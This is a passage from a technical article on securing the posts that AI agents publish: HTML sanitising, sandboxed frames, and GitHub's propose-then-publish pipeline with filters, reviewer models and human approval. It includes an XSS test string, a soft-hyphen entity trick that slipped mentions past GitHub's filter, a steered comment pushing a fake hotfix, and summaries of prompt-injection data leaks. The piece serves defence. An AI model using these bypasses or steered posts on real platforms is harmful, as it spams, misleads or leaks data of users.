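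Some programs try to remove unfinished symbols from the end of the text. Open WebUI's cleaning function, for instance, deletes a single `<` if it is the last character. This keeps a stray symbol from flickering on the screen but doesn't provide security, because the rule doesn't match longer fragments such as `<img src=`.

Even a harmless answer can briefly become live HTML while it streams. If the model explains the `<form>` tag, it puts the tag between backticks so that the page shows it as code. Until the second backtick arrives, a Markdown converter may treat the tag as real HTML. Sanitising all the text received so far each time more arrives removes a script in this position before the browser can run it, but doesn't prevent image leaks like GitLab Duo's if the sanitiser permits images.

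### Sandboxed frames

Some agents write small web pages, charts or programs that the user wants to see running. Sanitising would remove the scripts that make these work, so the chat window can display them in a frame, which is a separate page inside the main one. The frame's `sandbox` attribute blocks scripts, forms and access to the main page unless the developer allows them:

```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts" src="https://preview.example/123"></iframe>
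```

With this setting, a script in the preview can run, but the browser treats it as if it came from an unrelated website, so it can't read the chat or use the reader's login.

Corgea's *Open WebUI has stored XSS via the HTML renedering view* reports that Open WebUI 0.5.4 combined `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin` in its sandboxed preview frame. `allow-same-origin` lets the preview count as part of the site it came from. If the chat is on the same site, a script with both permissions can read the chat page's data and even remove the sandbox.

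Serving previews from a separate domain protects against this mistake. A script that has both permissions can then access only the preview domain, which should have no logins or private data. The company shouldn't use that domain for anything else, and previews for different users shouldn't be able to read each other's stored data.

LibreChat's flaw with quotation marks let injected code run inside a preview frame, according to the record from MITRE, which manages the CVE catalogue. The record rates the technical impact as "partial", which fits a script confined to a frame, though how much the script could reach depends on the frame's settings.

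A sandbox also doesn't protect the data inside the preview. If the support agent writes a chart with customers' names and sales figures, a hostile script in the chart can read them and send them to another server unless a content security policy blocks the request. The frame can also show a fake login form that gives the script any password a reader types. The chat window should therefore label the preview as agent-made content and never ask for a password there.

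## Checking an agent's posts before they are published

A company's integration can neutralise mentions, turn off previews and sanitise markup only in posts that pass through it. An agent that holds the platform's access token can post directly and skip these checks. GitHub Agentic Workflows, GitHub's system for running AI agents on a code repository, prevents this by not giving the agent the token. The agent only proposes posts, and a separate program checks and publishes them.

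### An agent that can only propose

GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) describes the design. The agent runs in a job whose token can read the repository but can't change it. To comment on an issue, the agent calls a tool named `add_comment`. The tool can't write to GitHub either. It only adds a line to a file:

```
{"type":"add_comment","body":"Another customer reports this problem."}
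```

After the agent finishes, a second job downloads the file, checks each line and publishes what passes. This job can write to GitHub, but it doesn't use a language model, so it can't follow a planted instruction. Its permissions cover only the kinds of output the developer has turned on, so a job that only creates issues can't change code.

An attacker who takes complete control of the agent can put anything in the file, but can't publish anything the second job rejects. By default, the attacker also can't choose where a comment appears, because the second job posts it to the issue or pull request that started the run and ignores any other number in the proposal.

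The separation protects only services whose credentials the agent lacks. If a developer also gives the agent a Slack tool with its own token, the agent's Slack messages bypass all these checks.

### The checks in order

A proposal goes through these stages, and a failure at any of them keeps it from being posted:

1. **Schema check.** The job refuses a proposal with missing or wrongly typed fields, such as a comment without a body.
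2. **Count limits.** The default is one comment per run. If the limit is three and the agent proposes four, the job publishes none of them.
3. **Sanitising.** The job neutralises mentions, commands and markup in the text.
4. **Domain filtering.** It replaces links to domains that aren't on the list.
5. **Repository check.** It refuses to post in another repository unless the developer has allowed that.
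6. **Posting.** It fills in the numbers of any issues it has just created, then sends the text to GitHub.

A single comment may contain at most 10 mentions, 50 links and 65,536 characters, including a footer that the job adds. The `add_comment` tool checks these limits when the agent proposes the comment and returns an error showing which one it exceeded, so the agent can shorten the text. The second job checks them again in case someone has changed the file directly.

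The limits apply to each run separately. If an outsider can start a run by opening an issue, ten issues could produce ten comments with 100 mentions in total, so a team also needs to limit how often people can start the agent.

To sanitise a post, the job first removes invisible characters, then filters links, escapes slash commands, escapes mentions and cleans up HTML. If it looked for mentions first, it would miss an at sign separated from a name by a zero-width space, and removing the space afterwards would create a working mention.

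GitHub's specification escapes a slash command only at the start of the text. The support agent quoted `/merge 812` on the third line of its comment, so the rule would not escape it and the merge bot would still act on it.

### One comment through the filter

Suppose the support agent proposes this comment. Sam is a customer with no role in the repository and no connection to the issue.

```
@sam reports the same problem (ticket 4471). fixes #123
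Log file: https://logs.example/4471
<script>alert(1)</script>
```

With default settings, the published comment would probably look like this in its source form:

```
`@sam` reports the same problem (ticket 4471). fixes #123
Log file: (redacted)
(script)alert(1)(/script)
```

GitHub's *Security Architecture* shows these replacements for text sent to the agent, and GitHub's user reference, *Safe Outputs*, describes similar rules for posts. Backticks around `@sam` make GitHub display it as code, so Sam gets no notification. The script tag becomes text in round brackets. GitHub removes scripts from comments anyway, but the replacement also protects other pages that copy the comment.

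The phrase "fixes #123" is probably published unchanged. According to the architecture page, it is a bot trigger and is put in backticks, but according to the user reference, the first ten bot triggers in a post are left unchanged. In a comment, the phrase only adds a link to issue 123, but in a pull request's description it is a closing keyword. A developer can escape every trigger by setting `max-bot-mentions` to 0, or escape all issue references by setting `allowed-github-references` to an empty list.

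Backticks stop GitHub from acting on a mention, but they may not stop a bot from responding to its trigger phrase. A bot that runs a plain text search for the phrase will still find it inside the backticks.

The job also adds a footer with the workflow's name and a link to the run, so readers know that an AI wrote the comment and the team can trace a bad post more easily.

### Who the agent may mention

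GitHub has no equivalent of Discord's `allowed_mentions` field, so the job has to find each mention in the text and decide whether to escape it. According to GitHub's user reference, the job leaves a mention active if the person is a collaborator on the repository where the post will appear, or is the issue's author or an assignee.

A developer can add named accounts or whole teams to the allowlist. For a team, the second job looks up the current members when it runs and leaves out bot accounts. It does these lookups with a separate read-only token, which the agent never receives. Setting `mentions: false` escapes every mention.

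GitHub's specification is stricter about comments. It exempts only the author of the issue or pull request and the names the developer has configured, so other collaborators are not exempt by default.

If the user reference is right, the default protects strangers from unwanted mentions better than it protects staff. In a repository with 200 collaborators, an attacker could try to make the agent mention any ten of them in one comment. The support agent only needs to alert Dana, so the company should turn off the exemptions for collaborators and participants and list Dana's account by name.

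### The default for outside links

GitHub's documents conflict on what happens to outside links when the developer sets no list of allowed domains. In version 1.29.8 of GitHub's specification, dated 1 October 2026, the list is empty by default, and an empty list means no filtering. According to the user reference, only GitHub's own domains are allowed by default. According to the architecture page, the list comes from the workflow's network settings and automatically includes GitHub's domains.

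The user reference and the architecture page probably describe the software more accurately than the specification, since both describe the filter as on by default. The specification is a working draft and also differs from the user reference on other points. For example, it accepts `http://` links, which the user reference excludes, and rejects patterns such as `org/*` in the list of permitted repositories, which the user reference allows.

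The default matters more now that posts may contain `<img>` tags, a change GitHub announced in its release notes for version 0.71.4. If domain filtering were off, an attacker could try to make the agent post a picture whose address contained private data, and GitHub's image proxy would deliver the data when it fetched the picture.

Instead of relying on the default, developers can set `allowed-domains` themselves and then test it by proposing a comment that links to a domain not on the list. They should keep the list short, because it also controls which links the agent sees in incoming issues. If a company adds its log server so that the agent can link to it, the agent will also see links to that server in strangers' issues.

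### A mention hidden behind an HTML name

In May 2026, an automatically generated bug report, issue 31702 in the project's tracker, described a way to get a mention past the filter using the soft hyphen, an invisible character that marks where a long word may break at the end of a line. HTML has a numeric code for this character, `&#173;`, and a named one, `&shy;`. The filter recognized only the numeric code.

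| Proposed text | After decoding | After removing invisible characters | Result |
| - | - | - | - |
| `@&#173;sam` | `@`, soft hyphen, `sam` | `@sam` | escaped |
| `@&shy;sam` | `@&shy;sam` | `@&shy;sam` | not escaped |

The filter recognised a mention only if a letter or digit followed the at sign. In the second row, an ampersand follows the at sign, so the filter left the text unchanged. GitHub's web page then converts `&shy;` into the invisible character, and readers see what looks like an ordinary `@sam`. Four other names for invisible characters worked the same way.

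The report warned that Sam might be notified, but its test ran only the filter and posted nothing to GitHub. Invisible characters normally disable a mention, so Sam would be notified only if GitHub removed the soft hyphen before looking for mentions. The test showed that the filter and the web page processed the same text differently, which is a flaw whether or not Sam would be notified.

The report tested version 0.68.3. The project's blog, GitHub's *Agent of the Day* (2026), dates version 0.72.1 to 7 May, so newer releases may already have behaved differently. The sanitising steps in the October specification don't include decoding named entities, and it is unclear whether GitHub has fixed the flaw. Anyone who depends on the filter can check by proposing a comment that contains `@&shy;` followed by the name of a test account.

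In February 2026, GitHub had already closed another route that used HTML entities to get mentions past the filter, and it later fixed the numeric form of the soft hyphen. It had also added fuzz tests for the mention filter in version 0.33.2. These tests feed a program large numbers of unusual inputs, but they find a flaw only if one of those inputs triggers it.

The suggested repair shows why handling names one at a time is unreliable. It added seven names, including `&wj;` for the word joiner character, but HTML has no such name. The correct name is `&NoBreak;`, which the repair left out.

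A filter can miss many of HTML's named character references. HTML defines 2,231 of them, but the standard decoding function in the programming language PHP recognised only 1,511, according to a proposal on PHP's wiki. The proposal recommends that a decoder handle "only the specified character references, and all of them".

To catch every mention, a filter has to decode text exactly as the renderer will. A complete list of HTML entity names isn't enough, because formats apply them differently. For instance, a browser accepts `&shy` without the semicolon in HTML text, but Markdown requires the semicolon. The safest method is to convert the post with the same software that the platform uses and look for mentions in the result. A simpler method is to escape every ampersand outside code, so that readers see `@&shy;sam` as typed. This also disables entities that the agent uses legitimately, but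 it rarely needs entities because it can write most characters directly.

Decoding can also create a flaw if the program publishes the decoded text. A tag written as `&lt;script&gt;` is harmless until a program decodes it and inserts the result into a page. Apostrophe CMS's *sanitize-html allowedTags Bypass via Entity-Decoded Text Leading to Stored XSS* describes this flaw in versions up to 2.17.2 of a widely used sanitiser. A filter should decode a copy of the text for its checks, then escape whatever it publishes.

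### What well-formed text can still do

None of these checks can tell whether a post is true. Suppose an attacker steers the support agent into proposing this comment:

```
Version 4.2 fixes this problem. Until then, please install
https://github.com/exports-helper/hotfix as administrator.
```

The comment contains no mention, command or HTML. Its only link passes the default domain filter because it leads to GitHub, where anyone can publish a program. Customers who read the comment under the company's name may well install the attacker's software.

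A post can also reveal private information in ordinary prose. Before GitHub saves the agent's files, it searches them for the exact values of the workflow's secrets, such as API keys, and masks them. This catches a copied key, but not one that the agent has encoded or written backwards. A customer's email address isn't one of the workflow's secrets, so the search doesn't look for it.

GitHub's specification addresses part of this problem with a rule based on where data comes from. By default, a workflow that can read private repositories may not send their contents to public ones. The rule works even if the agent rephrases the data. To protect customer records in the same way, the company would have to block public posting by any agent that reads them.

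The specification recommends monitoring, anomaly detection and periodic review for misleading posts that stay within the limits. GitHub's blog gives an example from the project's own repository, where an agent called AI Moderator labels new contributions and hides comments that break the rules. In May 2026 the monitoring system flagged one of its runs because the agent had taken 16 steps, while a comparison run that day had taken none. With a baseline of zero, almost any run would look unusual. The warning was also about how much work the agent did, which is weak evidence of whether its posts were accurate.

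### A second model as reviewer

GitHub Agentic Workflows can also have a second model review the proposals before the write job starts. According to GitHub's architecture page, this model receives the proposed posts, any code changes and the original task. It checks for leaked secrets, malicious code and actions outside the task, then labels the proposals safe or unsafe. It has no write permission. Developers can add their own instructions, such as checking for internal server addresses, and can also run conventional security scanners alongside the model.

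The reviewer could catch the false advice about the hotfix by comparing the comment with the task. It might notice that nobody asked the agent to recommend a download. It could also recognise a customer's address as private without a list of customers.

But the reviewer reads text that an attacker may have influenced, so a planted instruction can target it too. By default, the reviewer uses the same AI engine as the agent. If both run the same model, wording that misleads one is more likely to mislead the other. A team can reduce this risk by choosing a different model for the review and showing it only the proposed post and the task, not the stranger's ticket. But then the reviewer can't check the post against the ticket.

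GitHub's description of the reviewer gives no figures for how many bad posts it catches or how many good ones it blocks. In PromptArmor's mock bank application, a second model blocked an image that would have leaked data, but in EchoLeak, Microsoft's classifier let the attacker's email through. These are single cases, so they don't establish a detection rate.

A review can also fail because of formatting. The reviewing model writes its verdict as a line of text, which ordinary code then has to find. GitHub's release notes for version 0.85.0 describe a change that lets this code accept a verdict in bold or italics. Before that, the code could apparently miss a correct verdict because the model had added asterisks.

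Normally, a bad verdict stops the workflow and nothing is published. If the workflow is set to warn mode, the job blocks some actions, such as merging a pull request or adding labels, but still publishes comments and new issues with a prominent caution. It also publishes them, with a different warning, if the review itself fails. A caution helps people who read the comment, but by then GitHub has sent any notifications and another bot may have acted on the text. Warn mode is therefore unsuitable for posts that can trigger automated actions.

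### Approval by a person

A person can also approve posts after the agent proposes them and before the write job runs. GitHub's user reference explains how to assign the write job to a protected environment, a GitHub feature that can require a named reviewer's approval before a job starts. The job can't use the credentials stored in that environment until a reviewer approves it.

The approval covers the whole job, so a reviewer can't accept one comment and reject another from the same run. The reviewer also has to open the run to read the proposed text, and someone in a hurry may approve without doing so.

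GitHub offers a staged mode for trials, in which the job writes a preview of each post instead of publishing it. A developer can apply it to only some outputs, such as previewing pull requests while publishing comments normally. Staged mode suits a new agent whose behavior the team doesn't know yet. The job won't publish any output of a staged type until the developer turns the mode off, so staged mode can't be used to approve individual posts.

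People can judge things that a filter or model lacks the information to check, such as whether version 4.2 fixes the problem, but they may miss that an attacker has steered the agent. Microsoft's *Securing CI/CD in agentic world* (2026) reports that attackers hid instructions in HTML comments in public repositories. Browsers don't show these comments, so reviewers need to see the source text of both the issue and the proposed post.

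Manual approval also takes time, and GitHub's specification rejects it as a general solution because it creates bottlenecks and removes the benefit of automation. That objection is fair for routine comments but weaker for rare posts with serious consequences. The software company could use only the filter for comments in its private tracker, add a model review for public comments, and require a person's approval for anything that merges code or tells customers to install something.

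If the reviewing model blocks a harmless post, someone with administrator or maintainer access can still have GitHub publish the saved proposals from that run. They should read the proposals first, because this can also publish an attack that the model caught.

### Doing the same on Slack and Discord

A Slack or Discord integration can use the same design. The agent sends its proposals to a small posting service, and only that service holds the bot's token. GitHub already works this way with several outside services, including the issue trackers Jira and Linear. Its write job holds their credentials, and comments on Linear can go only to an issue the developer has chosen in advance.

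If a company runs its agent on GitHub and writes a custom job to post to Slack, that job would need its own sanitising. GitHub's filter follows GitHub's rules, so developers shouldn't expect it to handle Slack's `<!channel>` correctly.

For the support agent, a proposal could be as simple as this:

```
{"text": "@everyone Ticket 4471: exports fail.", "urgent": true}
```

The proposal has no field for a channel or a list of people to notify. The service takes both from its own settings and sends Discord this request:

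```
{
  "content": "<@5678> @everyone Ticket 4471: exports fail.",
  "allowed_mentions": {"users": ["5678"]}
}
```

The service added Dana's ID because the ticket is urgent, so Discord alerts Dana. Discord treats `@everyone` as plain text. An attacker who makes the agent mark every ticket as urgent can annoy Dana but can't reach anyone else.

On Slack, the service would escape the three special characters, turn off both kinds of preview and set `verbatim` if it uses layout blocks. On either platform, it should also remove links to domains outside its list, since a colleague could still click one.

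GitHub's limit of ten mentions per comment would be little use here, because a single `@everyone` on Discord can notify thousands of people and GitHub has no equivalent. The service should limit who can receive an alert, and limit messages per hour as well as per run so that an attacker can't get around the per-run limit by sending many tickets.

The Jira output avoids much of the filtering. The agent supplies plain text, and GitHub's code turns it into Jira's structured document format, keeping only paragraphs and line breaks. Slack's rich text blocks allow something similar, because they store ordinary text and mentions as separate elements. The service can put the model's words in text elements and add any mention itself.

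If a person has to approve messages, the service might post each draft in a private review channel with an "Approve" button. The draft needs the same protection as the final message, because a link preview could otherwise leak data before the reviewer has read the draft.
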